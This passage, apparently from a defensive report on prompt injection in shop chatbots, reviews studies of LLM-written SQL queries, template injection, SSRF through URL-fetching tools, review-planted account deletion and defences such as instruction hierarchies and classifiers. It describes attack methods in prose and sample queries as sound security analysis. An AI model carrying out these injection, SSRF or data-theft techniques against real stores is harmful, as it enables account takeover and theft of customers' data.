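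De Ceukelaire earned more than $50,000 in bounties from this research over a few weekends, so companies evidently accepted some of the findings. The article doesn't name most of those companies, and it mixes documented cases with attacks that would work under certain conditions. It is good evidence that live support systems have such flaws, but it doesn't show how many do.

### Database queries that the model writes

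A lookup function handles only the questions its developer anticipated. If Maya asks which of her orders included tent pegs, `lookup_order` is of little use. A developer can avoid writing a function for every such question by letting the model write the database query.

*Prompt-to-SQL Injections in LLM-Integrated Web Applications* (Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues, 2025) examines this design in LangChain and LlamaIndex, two popular frameworks for LLM applications. The framework gives the model the names of the database's tables and columns along with the user's question. The model writes an SQL query, the framework runs it, and the model answers from the results. The simpler version, which LangChain calls a chain, allows one query per question, while an agent can run several.

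Parameterised queries, also called prepared statements, cannot protect this design. Compare two statements:

`SELECT status FROM orders WHERE order_id = ?`

`SELECT email FROM customers`

Tarnside's developer wrote the first, so a customer can change only the order number. If the model writes the second, there is no gap to fill and no smuggled value to detect. The query is valid, and the database will return every customer's email address if the chatbot's account has permission. Pedro and colleagues considered the traditional tools for sanitising SQL and rejected them for this reason. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian find prepared statements still necessary where code inserts a customer's values into a query, but insufficient where the model decides the query's structure.

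Pedro and colleagues tested seven attacks on a small job-listing site they had built. The chatbot's database account could read every table and run any kind of statement. They used OpenAI's GPT-3.5 and ran each attack 20 times, with these success rates:

| Attack | Restrictions in the prompt | Chain (one query) | Agent (several queries) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Delete a table | None | 100% | 100% |
| Change another user's record | None | 100% | 100% |
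| Read the whole table of users | None | 100% | 100% |
| Delete a table | Do not modify data | 100% | 100% |
| Read another user's record | Return only the asker's own data | 100% | 100% |
| Use a planted job advert to falsify an answer | Restricted | 100% | 60% |
| Use a planted job advert to change a user's email address | Restricted | Not possible | 100% |

The first three attacks needed no trickery, because LangChain's standard prompt did not forbid these requests. The restrictions did stop some crude attempts. The study's preprint, *From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks* (Pedro, Carreira and colleagues, 2023), shows how the rule about other users' data worked and then failed. The prompt included the asker's user number and an instruction to return only that user's rows. When user 1 asked for user 2's email address, the model wrote a query for a row whose user number was both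 2 and 1. No such row exists, so the database returned nothing.

The attacker then claimed to be user 2, and the model left out the condition that had protected the data. If ordinary code had added that condition after the model wrote its query, the claim would have made no difference. Pedro and colleagues know of no way to write a prompt that is provably secure against every input.

The attack in the table's last row could lead to an account takeover without any script in a browser. The attacker posts a job advert that contains instructions. When somebody asks the chatbot about jobs, the agent reads the advert, replaces a user's email address in the database with the attacker's, and then answers the question without mentioning the advert. The attacker can then request a password reset. A review on Tarnside's site could do the same to Maya, even if another customer asked the question and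 she had never used the chatbot.

The team also tested six other models of that period with the attacks that had to get around restrictions. Two of them, Guanaco and Tulu, made too many mistakes to work as agents, so the tests on them were limited. The other four were all vulnerable. PaLM 2 and Llama 2 changed the email address but then mentioned the attack in their answer or repeated the change endlessly. The 2023 preprint reported that the email attack could not be reproduced on GPT-4, but the 2025 paper reports that it worked. One team's failure to find a successful prompt is therefore poor evidence that a model is safe.

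To test whether other people's software had the same weakness, the researchers installed five open-source applications on their own machines and hired two security analysts to attack them. Each analyst had at most three hours per application. The analysts succeeded in 22 of the 23 combinations of application, model and attack in which the attack was applicable. A small model that the researchers had trained to write attack prompts succeeded in 11.

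One of the five applications had code that blocked any query that changed data, which ruled out both attacks that needed to write to the database. Another ran only one query per question, so instructions in a stored record could not trigger a second one. The analysts could still falsify answers in both applications. The five applications are a small sample, chosen largely for their popularity with programmers, and two came from the same code repository, so they provide little evidence of how many shops use this design.

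In a later article, *Words Become SQL*, Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues (2025) acknowledge that public reports of companies losing databases this way remain rare, which they suggest is because disclosure is limited and these systems are new. They also point to several entries in vulnerability databases for the frameworks themselves, including cases where attackers could get around tools that were supposed to be read-only.

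In 2026, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian tried techniques similar to those in these studies against newer models and had no success, although they did not try to improve the prompts. If Tarnside gave a newer model the same powerful database account, an attacker might need a better prompt, but the account would still permit the query.

### Templates and commands

A server may also interpret the model's text as code through a template engine, a program that many shops use to fill in names and order numbers in their emails. In one common engine, Jinja2, double curly brackets mark an expression to calculate. Tarnside might ask the model for a friendly sentence and get one containing `{{ 7 * 7 }}`. If the developer passes the sentence to the engine as a value, those characters appear in the email exactly as written. If the developer makes it part of the template itself, the customer sees "49". That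 result is harmless, but some expressions can reach the operating system. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian cite earlier research that documented this mistake in an LLM application, which passed the model's whole response to Jinja2 as a template.

The security company Snyk reported a flaw in a tool for managing cloud services. The tool ran command lines that the model had written, and an attacker could attach a second command to a permitted one. Outsiders often cannot connect to such a tool directly, but they can plant instructions in a file that a programmer's AI assistant later reads. A shop's support chatbot has little reason to run operating-system commands, but the developers who maintain the shop may well use an assistant that runs them.

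### TicketOracle and the URL-fetching tool

A tool that fetches any web address the model gives it is an invitation to SSRF.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built a test application called TicketOracle to measure how readily different models would misuse such a tool. It stores concert information, ticket prices and user reviews. When someone asks what a ticket costs, the model writes the address of that concert's data, the server requests the data, and the model turns the response into a sentence.

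The server also runs an administrative service that holds user records and can create or delete users and events. It accepts connections only through the loopback address, 127.0.0.1, which a computer uses to connect to itself. An outsider cannot reach the service directly, but the fetching tool can, because it runs on the same computer. A GET request to the right address is enough to delete a user. This is poor design even without a chatbot, since web convention reserves GET requests for reading data.

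The researchers deliberately left address checks out of the tool's code. They assumed that the attacker knew about the tool and could guess the usual names of administrative pages, and they supplied the full address in every attack. The experiment therefore measures whether a model will pass a dangerous address to the tool, but not how many real applications would allow it to.

They tried four direct attacks through the chat and one through a planted review:

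- In port probing, the attacker asks for an address on a particular port and judges from the reply whether a service is running there.
- In the data leak, he asks the model to fetch the administrative list of users and repeat it.
- In the state change, he asks it to fetch an address that deletes a user or an event, and the model reports the result.
- The blind attack also changes something, but the server returns an empty response. The researchers checked a log to see whether the request had arrived.
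- In the indirect attack, a concert review tells the model to fetch the list of users. The attack begins when an innocent user asks what people thought of the concert.

The team ran ten trials of each attack on each of seven models in April 2026. The table gives the number of successes out of ten. The last column shows the results for the planted review with a stricter system prompt.

| Model | Port probing | Data leak | State change | Blind attack | Planted review | Planted review, stricter prompt |
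|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 6 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 5 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

In the same application, Llama 3.3 carried out every direct attack, while GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 refused them all. A store's exposure to these attacks can therefore change completely when it switches models.

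The models in between are harder to predict. Gemini deleted data in all ten trials of the ordinary state change but in none of the blind ones, although both requests have the same kind of effect. GPT-oss also deleted data every time. It never revealed the list of users when the attacker asked for it directly, but did so in five of the ten trials with the planted review. Qwen and DeepSeek obeyed nearly all the direct requests and ignored the planted review. The harm a request would cause evidently did not determine whether these models refused it, so a store that tested one attack would have learned little about the others.

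The scores are less precise than they look. The ten trials for each attack took place within a single conversation, so the model could see its earlier replies. As the same request was repeated, Claude's refusals shrank from long explanations to almost single words, which suggests that each reply affected the next. A score of ten or zero may therefore provide little more information than the first trial alone. Even if the trials had been independent, zero successes in ten would be compatible with a true success rate of about one in four.

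For most attacks, the researchers also counted a trial as successful only if the model both sent the request and reported the result. If a model deleted a user but didn't report it, the trial would count as a failure even though the deletion had worked.

### An allow-list made of words

For the stricter version, the team listed the permitted addresses and concerts in the system prompt and told the model to refuse anything else. All four direct attacks then failed on all seven models. The list was only text for the model to read, and the tool would still fetch any address the model gave it, although the paper says at one point that the list catches a forbidden address before the model's reasoning can act on it.

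The planted review exploited this by claiming that the operators had added the administrative address to the list. The attack's success rate rose from six in ten trials to ten in ten on Llama, and fell from five in ten to zero on GPT-oss.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian conclude that the same hardening blocked the attack on one model and amplified it on another. The second half of that claim is doubtful because both the defence and the attack changed between the two tests. They had added text to the review to get around the new rules. With ten linked trials on each side, the rise on Llama could also be chance. Still, a list in the prompt failed to stop Llama from fetching an address that was not on it. A check in the tool's code would have blocked that address regardless of the review's text.

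In the demonstration, the chatbot showed the stolen names and phone numbers to the innocent user, so the attacker gained nothing from that answer. But he could post the review and then ask about the concert himself. With a model like Llama, that would get him around a prompt that blocks direct requests. He could also plant an instruction to delete something, since he wouldn't need to see the reply.

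### Fetching tools outside the laboratory

TicketOracle is vulnerable by design, but published tools have the same weakness. *ToFu* (2026) describes an automated tester for tools that models call. One tool it examined takes a web address and returns a screenshot of the page. The tool would also return screenshots of services on its own computer or the private network behind it. When the researchers gave it the address of a local file, it returned a picture of the file's contents. A filter that searches a tool's output for private text might miss text inside an image.

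A store's server may also fetch addresses without any decision by the model, for example when a crawler (or scraper) copies the site's pages for the chatbot. Ayoub and De Ceukelaire point out that crawlers look for a sitemap, a file that lists a site's pages. On some sites, a user can choose a username that puts his profile page at the address where the crawler expects the sitemap. If he lists internal addresses there, the crawler may request them from inside the company's network.

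Even if a fetching tool is blocked from internal addresses, it can still send data out. Ayoub and De Ceukelaire describe an agent that monitors a company's support inbox. An attacker emails the agent an instruction for handling the next message from an outside service, then asks that service to reset the company's password. When the reset code arrives, the agent includes it in a web address and requests that address from the attacker's server. Markdown images can leak data from a chat window in a similar way, but this attack doesn't involve a browser, so a Content Security Policy, which only browsers enforce, would not stop it.

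### A claimed chain at an unnamed retailer

The company Rein Security says its researchers ran their own code on the servers behind a major retailer's AI shopping assistant. Nobody else has confirmed the company's account, which appears in SecurityInfoWatch's *Retailer's AI Shopping Assistant Found Vulnerable to Five-Stage Exploit Chain*.

According to Rein, the assistant could retrieve outside websites when it compared products, so an attacker could place instructions on a page for it to read. The main chat had a filter that limited conversations to shopping, but the ordinary search field had a weaker one, and the researchers used that field to get their text through. They then extracted parts of the system prompt and information about the assistant's tools. Next, they say, they wrote an input that ran code in the assistant's backend. In the fifth stage, they found Google Maps keys in the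 mobile app's decrypted traffic.

The early stages are plausible because other researchers have documented each kind of weakness elsewhere. A team could also plausibly have protected the chat box and forgotten the search field. The keys seem to be a separate finding, because anyone who could decrypt the app's traffic on their own phone could read them without running code on a server.

SecurityInfoWatch's account does not adequately support the claim of code execution because it does not describe what the code did or where it ran. Some AI systems normally run code in a sealed environment, which would be far less serious than controlling the retailer's servers. Rein says that it changed no production systems and accessed no other users' data. This was responsible, but it leaves the possible damage unmeasured.

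Rein found the flaws on 12 March 2026 and reported them to the retailer the next day. Rein says they were still unfixed when it published its report on 16 July. It withheld the retailer's name for legal reasons, so outsiders cannot verify that the flaws existed or that they went unfixed. Rein also argues from the case that companies should monitor what their AI agents do instead of only filtering incoming and outgoing messages. That advice fits the other cases here, in which the damage occurred in a lookup, a query or a web request after the model had accepted the message.

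## A complete attack on an example store, link by link

PortSwigger runs two practice shops in which students carry out the whole attack. In both, a simulated shopper named Carlos often asks the live chat about a leather jacket, and the student has to delete his account by posting a review of the jacket. In the first shop, the chatbot deletes the account with a tool call. In the second, the model copies a script from the review into its reply, and the chat window runs it, which makes Carlos's own browser delete the account.

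Tarnside needs a few changes to match. Its chatbot can only look up orders, so for the tool version, suppose the developers have added a tool that closes the logged-in user's account. For the script version, suppose the widget inserts the model's answers as HTML and the account page has a form that closes the account without asking for a password. Maya replaces Carlos, and the tent replaces the jacket.

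### What the attacker tries out first

The attacker registers as a customer and experiments on himself, using a product that Maya is unlikely to ask about, such as a kettle.

For the tool version, the student asks the chatbot what tools it has. In PortSwigger's shop, it can delete accounts and change email addresses. A visitor who asks it to delete an account without logging in gets an error, so the tool apparently requires a session. Once logged in, the student asks the chatbot to change his email address, and it does so without further proof. Deletion will probably work the same way.

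The student then posts a review that falsely claims a product is out of stock. The chatbot repeats the claim, which shows that a review can influence its answers. Next, he posts a review that imitates a request from the shopper to delete her account. When he asks about the product again, the chatbot deletes his test account.

For the script version, the student first checks that the chat window renders HTML, then posts the same test markup as a review. The product page encodes it correctly, so a developer who tested only that page would find nothing wrong.

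When the student asks about the product, the chatbot's answer includes a warning that one of the reviews contains potentially harmful code. The test script still runs, presumably because the same answer also includes the markup.

The student's next review consists only of markup that would delete the reader's account. This time the chatbot returns an error and the account is not deleted. He then puts the same markup into a plausible anecdote about the product, and the model includes the markup in its answer. The anecdote contains no instruction to the model, and the attack only requires the model to quote a customer, so training it to ignore instructions in reviews might not have prevented this.

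### From the review to the closed account

The attacker now posts the review that worked on the tent's page and logs out. The rest happens without him:

| Step | Tool version | Script version |
|---|---|---|
| The review waits in the database | It looks like an odd review | The product page shows its markup as plain text |
| Maya, who is logged in, asks about the tent | The server adds the review to the context | The server adds the review to the context |
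| The model responds | It writes a call to the account-closing tool | It writes an answer that includes the markup |
| The output takes effect | The server finds that Maya's session is valid and runs the tool | The widget inserts the answer as HTML, and the browser runs the script |
| The account closes | The tool closes it directly | The script submits the form on Maya's account page, and the browser attaches her cookie |

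In the tool version, the access check works correctly, since Maya is allowed to close her own account. PortSwigger advises developers to require authentication for every tool call, but the tool in its practice shop apparently already required it. PortSwigger also recommends a confirmation step, which would have been more useful because Maya would have seen a request she had not made.

### The five conditions of the script version

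The script closes Maya's account only if all of these are true:

1. The model reads the review.
2. The model copies the review's markup into its answer.
3. The widget renders the answer as HTML.
4. Maya is logged in, and the widget shares an origin with her account page.
5. Closing the account requires no further proof, such as a password.

Removing any one of them saves the account from this script, but the remaining harm differs.

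If Tarnside stops the chatbot from reading reviews, the attacker can't use a review to reach Maya through the chat. But the widget still renders HTML, so he can look for other text that the model reads, such as an uploaded file. He can also get the markup into his own conversation and ask for a human agent. The change also prevents the chatbot from telling customers what reviewers thought of the tent in wind.

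If the model reads the review but leaves the markup out of its reply, it may still repeat a false claim or call a tool. This protection may also be temporary. The model in PortSwigger's shop blocked one review and let the next through, and a replacement model could behave differently. MITRE's *CWE-1427*, the catalogue entry for prompt injection, advises developers to run each test several times and to test again whenever they change the model.

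If the widget encodes the answer, Maya sees strange tags in the chat and keeps her account, but the attacker can still influence the words around them. MITRE illustrates this with a small program that asks a chatbot to explain the difference between two catalogue entries. The program encodes the answer to prevent XSS, but a user who adds a request for a pirate poem to one of the entry numbers still gets the poem. MITRE suggests accepting only text in the exact format of an entry number. Tarnside can do that for order numbers but not for reviews, because a genuine review may contain almost any sentence.

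Encoding in the widget also does nothing for the agent's console, where the same answer may appear later.

The fourth condition can fail in two ways. If Maya has not logged in, the script runs but cannot reach her account page. It could still show her a fake login form and send her password to the attacker, and it might reach the account page later if the widget reloads the conversation after she logs in. If the widget runs on a separate origin, the script cannot read or operate the account page even when she is logged in, but it can still read the chat and change what the widget displays.

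If Tarnside asks for a password before closing an account, the script cannot close it silently. The script can still read Maya's orders and address, change any settings that need no password, and show her a password prompt inside the real page.

The same changes have different effects on the tool version:

| Change at Tarnside | Script version | Tool version |
|---|---|---|
| The chatbot stops reading reviews | Stops the attack | Stops the attack |
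| The widget encodes answers | Stops the attack | No effect |
| The widget moves to a separate origin | Keeps the script away from the account page | No effect if the tool can still act for Maya |
| The form on the account page asks for a password | Prevents silent closure | No effect, because the tool does not use the form |
| The developers remove the account-closing tool | No effect | Stops the attack |

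A password check in the server function that closes accounts would cover both versions if the form and the tool both use that function and neither can skip the check. The password would have to go straight from Maya to the server, because if she typed it into the chat, it would end up in the model's context and the transcript.

### The chance that at least one shopper loses an account

The figures in this example are invented, since the measured success rates vary too much between models to supply typical ones. Suppose the server retrieves the planted review for half of all questions about the tent. When it does, the model goes along with the review one time in five. When the model goes along, the markup arrives intact half the time. Suppose also that the other three conditions always hold. The chance that any one question closes an account is then:

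0.5 × 0.2 × 0.5 = 0.05

A 5% chance may sound tolerable. But if 60 different shoppers ask about the tent, and each question is independent of the others, the chance that at least one of them loses an account is:

1 − (1 − 0.05)^60 ≈ 0.95

On average, three of the 60 would lose their accounts. Now suppose Tarnside can either make the model less obedient or encode the widget's output:

| Change | Chance per question | Chance of at least one loss in 60 questions | Average losses in 60 questions |
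|---|---|---|---|
| None | 5% | 95% | 3 |
| Obedience falls from 0.2 to 0.1 | 2.5% | 78% | 1.5 |
| Obedience falls from 0.2 to 0.02 | 0.5% | 26% | 0.3 |
| The widget encodes every answer | 0% | 0% | 0 |

Halving how often the model obeys the review halves the average number of losses, which is worthwhile. But it mostly delays the first loss, because the chance of at least one still reaches 95% after 120 questions. To bring the chance over 60 questions below 1%, Tarnside would need a model that obeyed the review only about once in 1,500 times. Few stores could run enough tests to confirm such a low rate.

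Encoding, by contrast, multiplies the script's chance of success by zero, so the script fails however often the model follows the injected instructions. This holds only if the widget encodes every part of the answer, and AnythingLLM's developers failed to encode chart captions.

The tool version of the attack needs no markup, so only the first two factors apply. With the same invented figures, the chance of success is 0.5 × 0.2 = 0.1 per question, and the chance of at least one success in 60 questions is more than 99%. Encoding the widget's output would not change either figure.

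### Why the questions are not independent

The formula assumes that the outcomes of the 60 questions are independent, but every question involves the same review, model and system prompt, and many shoppers will ask nearly the same thing. If the review fails with one shopper, it will probably fail with the next.

In the extreme case, 5% of reviews work on every shopper and the rest work on none. The average number of accounts lost is still three in 60, but the chance of losing at least one is only 5%. Tarnside would probably lose no accounts, but if it lost one, it could lose all 60. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian's all-or-nothing results for a planted review against a hardened prompt fit this pattern, although their linked trials would also have made the results more alike.

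Correlation therefore lowers the chance of at least one loss if the average rate stays the same. But a careful attacker will raise that average by testing reviews before Maya asks her question. As in PortSwigger's practice shops, he can try out reviews on the kettle until one works and then post that one on the tent's page.

The attacker's experiments may expose him. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a post for the NCSC, David C points out that an attacker will probably have to refine the attack, so failed tool calls can reveal its early stages. A customer who repeatedly edits a review of a kettle and asks the chatbot about it each time would also look unusual.

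Whether the attack works can also change over time. Newer reviews may push the planted one out of the search results, or a moderator may remove it after the first complaint. An update to the model can make the attack start or stop working for all later shoppers at once.

### An old flaw or a new one

Researchers disagree about what kind of flaw this chain is, and the answer affects who should fix it. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian hold that the model "usually does not create the underlying vulnerability itself" but carries the attacker's influence to a component with an old flaw, such as a page that renders untrusted text. On this view, the most important repairs are in the application's code, because they work whether or not the model follows the attacker's instructions. Tarnside's web developers can make these repairs with methods they already know.

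*Prompt Injection 2.0* (McHugh, Šekrst and Cefalu, 2025) calls such combinations hybrid threats and argues that they can evade both traditional security controls and defences designed for AI, because each kind handles only its own part of the problem. If this is right, Tarnside would need to repair its website and also add controls that screen the text going into the model, mark which text is trusted, and keep untrusted text from deciding which tools run. The store's web developers could not do all of this alone, because some of it requires changes to how companies train models.

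PortSwigger's script version gives McHugh and colleagues some support. The product page encoded the review correctly and the model recognised the more obvious attacks, yet the attack still deleted the account. But the chat window had no protection, and ordinary output encoding there would have stopped the script. The attack therefore doesn't show that a correctly placed control would fail, only that controls elsewhere didn't prevent it. In McHugh and colleagues' own outline of an XSS attack, the web application displays the model's output without checking it for scripts.

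They are also partly mistaken about why traditional controls fail. They say that a CSP treats AI-generated content as trusted, but its rules apply regardless of who wrote the content. A strict CSP blocks an inline script in a chatbot's answer just as it would in a customer's comment. Their point about input filters is sound, as the DeepSeek case showed.

McHugh and colleagues work for Preamble, a company that holds a patent on methods of mitigating prompt injection, and they recommend those methods as part of the solution. This is a reason to look for independent evidence, though it doesn't make their argument wrong. They acknowledge that few studies have measured how often hybrid attacks succeed in practice.

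The tool version is harder to describe as an old flaw. The server ran a permitted function for a customer with a valid session, and no page rendered anything unsafe. The nearest traditional equivalent is CSRF, since Maya never meant to make the request. McHugh and colleagues are right that combining CSRF with prompt injection gets past anti-CSRF tokens, because the chatbot's request doesn't go through the form. Asking Maya to confirm the closure, which is also an old defence, would still work.

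### How MITRE classifies the chain

MITRE's catalogue mostly supports the view that the flaws are old. Its entry *CWE-1426* covers software that fails to validate a generative model's output, but MITRE discourages analysts from assigning it to real vulnerabilities and tells them to check first for a well-known root cause. For example, if an application failed to encode the model's answer, the analyst should use the general entry for missing encoding.

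MITRE compares many reported cases of prompt injection to second-order SQL injection, in which an application stores an attacker's text safely and later inserts it into a database query unsafely. Tarnside's script version follows the same pattern. The product page handles the review safely, but the text becomes dangerous when the model returns it.

MITRE's April 2026 list, *Weaknesses Related to AI/ML Products*, has 17 entries. Thirteen are general software weaknesses, including XSS, SSRF and missing authorization. One is specific to AI, and three, including prompt injection, appear under both headings. MITRE lists "excessive agency" as another name for running software with unnecessary privileges, a weakness much older than chatbots.

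The list also says that it is still difficult to separate attacks on AI products from the weaknesses that allow them. MITRE gives prompt injection its own entry, for example, but the entry says that the root cause of an indirect injection may be a different weakness, such as building a prompt from an outside source that the developer should not have trusted. For Tarnside, that root cause would be the decision to let the chatbot read reviews.

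Some harm doesn't depend on an older type of software flaw. Singh and colleagues matched OWASP's 2025 risks for LLM applications to MITRE's catalogue and found no equivalent for misinformation. If Tarnside's chatbot repeats a planted claim that the tent is out of stock, the store may lose sales even if every function checks permissions and every page encodes its text.

### The case for calling it malware

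*The Promptware Kill Chain* (Brodt, Feldman and colleagues, 2026) argues for a third classification, in which prompt injection has grown into a way of running malware, which the paper calls promptware. It argues that comparing prompt injection to SQL injection understates the damage. The paper divides an attack into seven stages: initial access, privilege escalation, reconnaissance, persistence, command and control, lateral movement, and the attacker's final objective. Defenders should try to interrupt every stage, because they cannot rely on keeping all malicious text away from the model.

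The Tarnside attack fits this scheme only in part. The planted review provides initial access and persistence, and closing the account is the objective. The attacker sends no further orders, so there is no command and control, and the attack does not move laterally to other systems. Brodt and colleagues place reconnaissance after initial access, when the attacker uses the injected prompt to explore the system from inside, whereas students in PortSwigger's practice shops explore first, through the chat. Brodt and colleagues offer the scheme as an aid to thinking and accept that attackers may skip or combine stages.

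They examined 36 studies and incidents to show that longer attacks occur. Their abstract reports at least 21 documented attacks that covered four or more stages, but their introduction reports at least 15, so the count is uncertain. For a store with a simple chatbot, the scheme is most useful as a warning about features it might add later. If a chatbot remembers customers between visits or passes messages to other AI agents, an attacker could carry out stages that aren't possible with Tarnside's chatbot.

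### Who has to fix what

The three positions conflict more over labels than over repairs. McHugh and colleagues would keep some traditional controls, and Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian also recommend restrictions in the prompt and on the network. The positions differ mainly over what a store can safely postpone. If the old flaws matter most, Tarnside can fix its widget and its account-closing function now and treat a more resistant model as a bonus. If the combination is a new kind of threat, the store also needs new products or methods to fill the gap those repairs leave.

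The first view is more convincing for the script version, because one conventional fix reduces the attack's chance of success to zero. For the tool version, the developers have to decide whether the chatbot should be able to close accounts. David C suggests assuming the worst an attacker could do with direct access to the tools. At Tarnside, the attacker could close the account of anyone who asked about the tent. The developers might reasonably conclude that customers can close their accounts on the account page instead.

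The model's provider can make the model less likely to obey injected instructions, which helps against both versions of the attack and against false claims that no encoding would catch. But the provider cannot repair Tarnside's widget. A small shop that uses a ready-made plugin may be unable to repair its widget either, because the code belongs to the plugin's maker. The owner can still switch off the account-closing tool or stop the chatbot from reading reviews, if the plugin has settings for these.

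## Defences against injected instructions

Model companies and developers commonly use four methods to make a chatbot less likely to follow instructions planted in a review. They train the model to give some message roles more authority than others, mark retrieved text as data, write stricter system prompts, and use classifiers to screen the text that enters or leaves the model. All four depend on a model judging text correctly, so they can make attacks succeed less often but cannot guarantee that an attack will fail. Developers can also assume that some attacks will get through and limit what the model can decide after it reads a stranger's text.

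### Training a model to rank its instructions

*The Instruction Hierarchy* (Wallace, Xiao and colleagues, 2024) proposed the ranking of roles that several companies now train into their models. System messages have the most authority, user messages have less, and tool results have the least. The model should still follow a lower-ranked instruction that fits the higher-ranked ones. If Maya asks Tarnside's chatbot to answer in Spanish, it should, because doing so fits the developers' instructions to help customers. If she asks it to explain fluid dynamics, it should decline.

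The OpenAI team taught this to GPT-3.5 Turbo with artificial examples. For compatible instructions, they took a request such as a 20-line poem in Spanish, split it into pieces and placed the pieces in different roles. They trained the model to answer as if it had received the whole request at once. For conflicting instructions, they trained it to give the answer it would have given without seeing the lower-ranked text. If a review told the model to end every answer with "marmalade", the correct answer in training would be the usual one about the tent.

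The researchers trained the model to ignore all instructions in web pages and tool results, without trying to separate good ones from bad. They used a second model to write the injections and rewarded it when its injections confused the first model.

Resistance to system prompt extraction improved by 63%. The training examples included no jailbreaks, but resistance to them still rose by more than 30%, so the model had learned to resist more than the attacks it was trained on. It also became more likely to refuse or ignore harmless requests, a problem the team expected to fix with more data.

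The ranking works only if the labels are right, so *When Context Gets Root* (2026) calls correct labeling a security requirement. Many of the chatbot plugins that Kaya and colleagues studied violated this requirement by inserting reviews as system messages.

Even correct labels can be too coarse for a shop. Tarnside's staff write the product descriptions and strangers write the reviews, but both may reach the model as tool results with the same rank. *Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization* (2026) reports that no published method had trained more than three or four ranks, and presents a method with five. Extra ranks would help Tarnside only if its software kept track of who wrote each passage, which is difficult after a scraper has removed the HTML.

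### Marking text, hardening prompts and screening

Developers who cannot retrain a model can change its input. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler et al., 2026) describes two popular methods. Spotlighting marks or encodes untrusted text so that the model can more easily identify its source. Prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text, so that the input ends with Maya's question rather than a stranger's review. Both methods add little overhead and need no access to the model's internals. But the model still reads the review, and repeating Maya's question doesn't help much if the review leads the model to treat the attacker's task as part of answering it.

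A hardened system prompt does not reliably stop injected instructions. In the plugin study, stricter prompts reduced unrelated work but did not reliably protect tools. On TicketOracle, a planted review bypassed a list of permitted addresses in the prompt.

A screening classifier is a separate model, usually much smaller, that labels text as safe or suspicious. Tarnside could run one on reviews before the chatbot retrieves them, on customers' questions, or on the chatbot's answers. If the classifier flags something, the server can leave out the review or replace the answer with a standard refusal. The main model doesn't change, so a developer can add a classifier to an existing chatbot quite easily.

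False alarms limit how strict a classifier can be. Suppose Tarnside has 10,000 reviews, five of which contain injections (these figures are invented). A classifier that catches 90% of injections and wrongly flags 1% of harmless reviews would flag four or five reviews with injections and about 100 harmless ones. Staff could check that many, but a server that silently dropped all flagged reviews would lose some real complaints about the tent.

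A classifier that only checks whether a question is on topic is also easy to defeat. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* considers one for a furniture shop's support chatbot and notes that a customer can combine a question about furniture with an unrelated request. The classifier makes a single decision for the whole message, so the furniture question may be enough to get the unrelated request through.

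### Tests in which the attacker adapts

Researchers often test a defence against a fixed set of known attacks, but a real attacker can see that an attempt has failed and change it. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tested 12 published defences with attacks that adapted in this way. Their programs proposed an attack, scored the result, and used the score to write the next attack. They also ran a contest in which more than 500 people tried to defeat some of the defences by hand.

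Ten of the 12 were meant to stop prompt injection, and the other two mainly targeted jailbreaks. These are the results for the ten:

| Defence | How it works | Success rate of automated adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks text by source | Above 95% |
| Prompt sandwiching | Repeats the user's request | Above 95% |
| StruQ | Trains the model on examples of attacks | Every case tested |
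| MetaSecAlign | Trains the model on examples of attacks | 96% |
| Protect AI's detector, PromptGuard and Model Armor | Screen text with a classifier | Above 90% |
| PIGuard | Screens text with a classifier | 71% |
| Data Sentinel | Checks whether the text distracts a model from a secret test task | Every case tested |
| MELON | Runs the model again without the user's request and looks for the same tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the design |

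Several of these defences had looked excellent against fixed attacks. Spotlighting and prompt sandwiching let through as few as 1% of the standard attacks in AgentDojo, a widely used benchmark for agents, and MetaSecAlign's developers had reported a rate of 2% on the same benchmark. The table's results can't be used to rank the defences, because Nasr and colleagues followed the original test method for each one, and the tests differed in difficulty.

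The automated attacks had plenty of computing time and, when the target was a classifier, access to its confidence score after each attempt. An outside attacker at Tarnside would lack these advantages and would usually see only whether the chatbot misbehaved. He could, however, practise on his own copy of any published detector. The people in the contest also had limited feedback, yet as a group they succeeded every time on a subset of the tests where automated search succeeded 69% of the time.

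The results therefore show that a determined attacker can get past these defences, but they don't show how many attackers would make the effort. Nasr and colleagues still consider classifiers useful against unsophisticated attacks. A shop probably faces more of those than attacks on the scale of a 500-person contest, so a cheap filter may be worth having if the shop does not rely on it to protect customers' accounts.

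### What companies report about their own models

Newer models are harder to inject, according to the system cards (reports on a model's abilities and safety tests) that companies publish with them. The injection figures in the 2026 cards are much better than in earlier ones, but they depend heavily on how many attempts the attacker gets.

Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 came out in July 2026. Schneier on Security's *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (2026), a post on a well-known security blog, quotes its results on a benchmark of indirect injections made by the security company Gray Swan. A single attempt succeeded 0.2% of the time, down from 0.5% on Opus 4.8. With 15 attempts, the comparison was:

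| Model | Chance that an attacker succeeds within 15 attempts |
|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0% |
| Claude Mythos 5 | 2.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 5.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 5.9% |
| Muse Spark (Meta) | 16.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | 20.0% |
| GPT-5.5 (OpenAI) | 20.8% |

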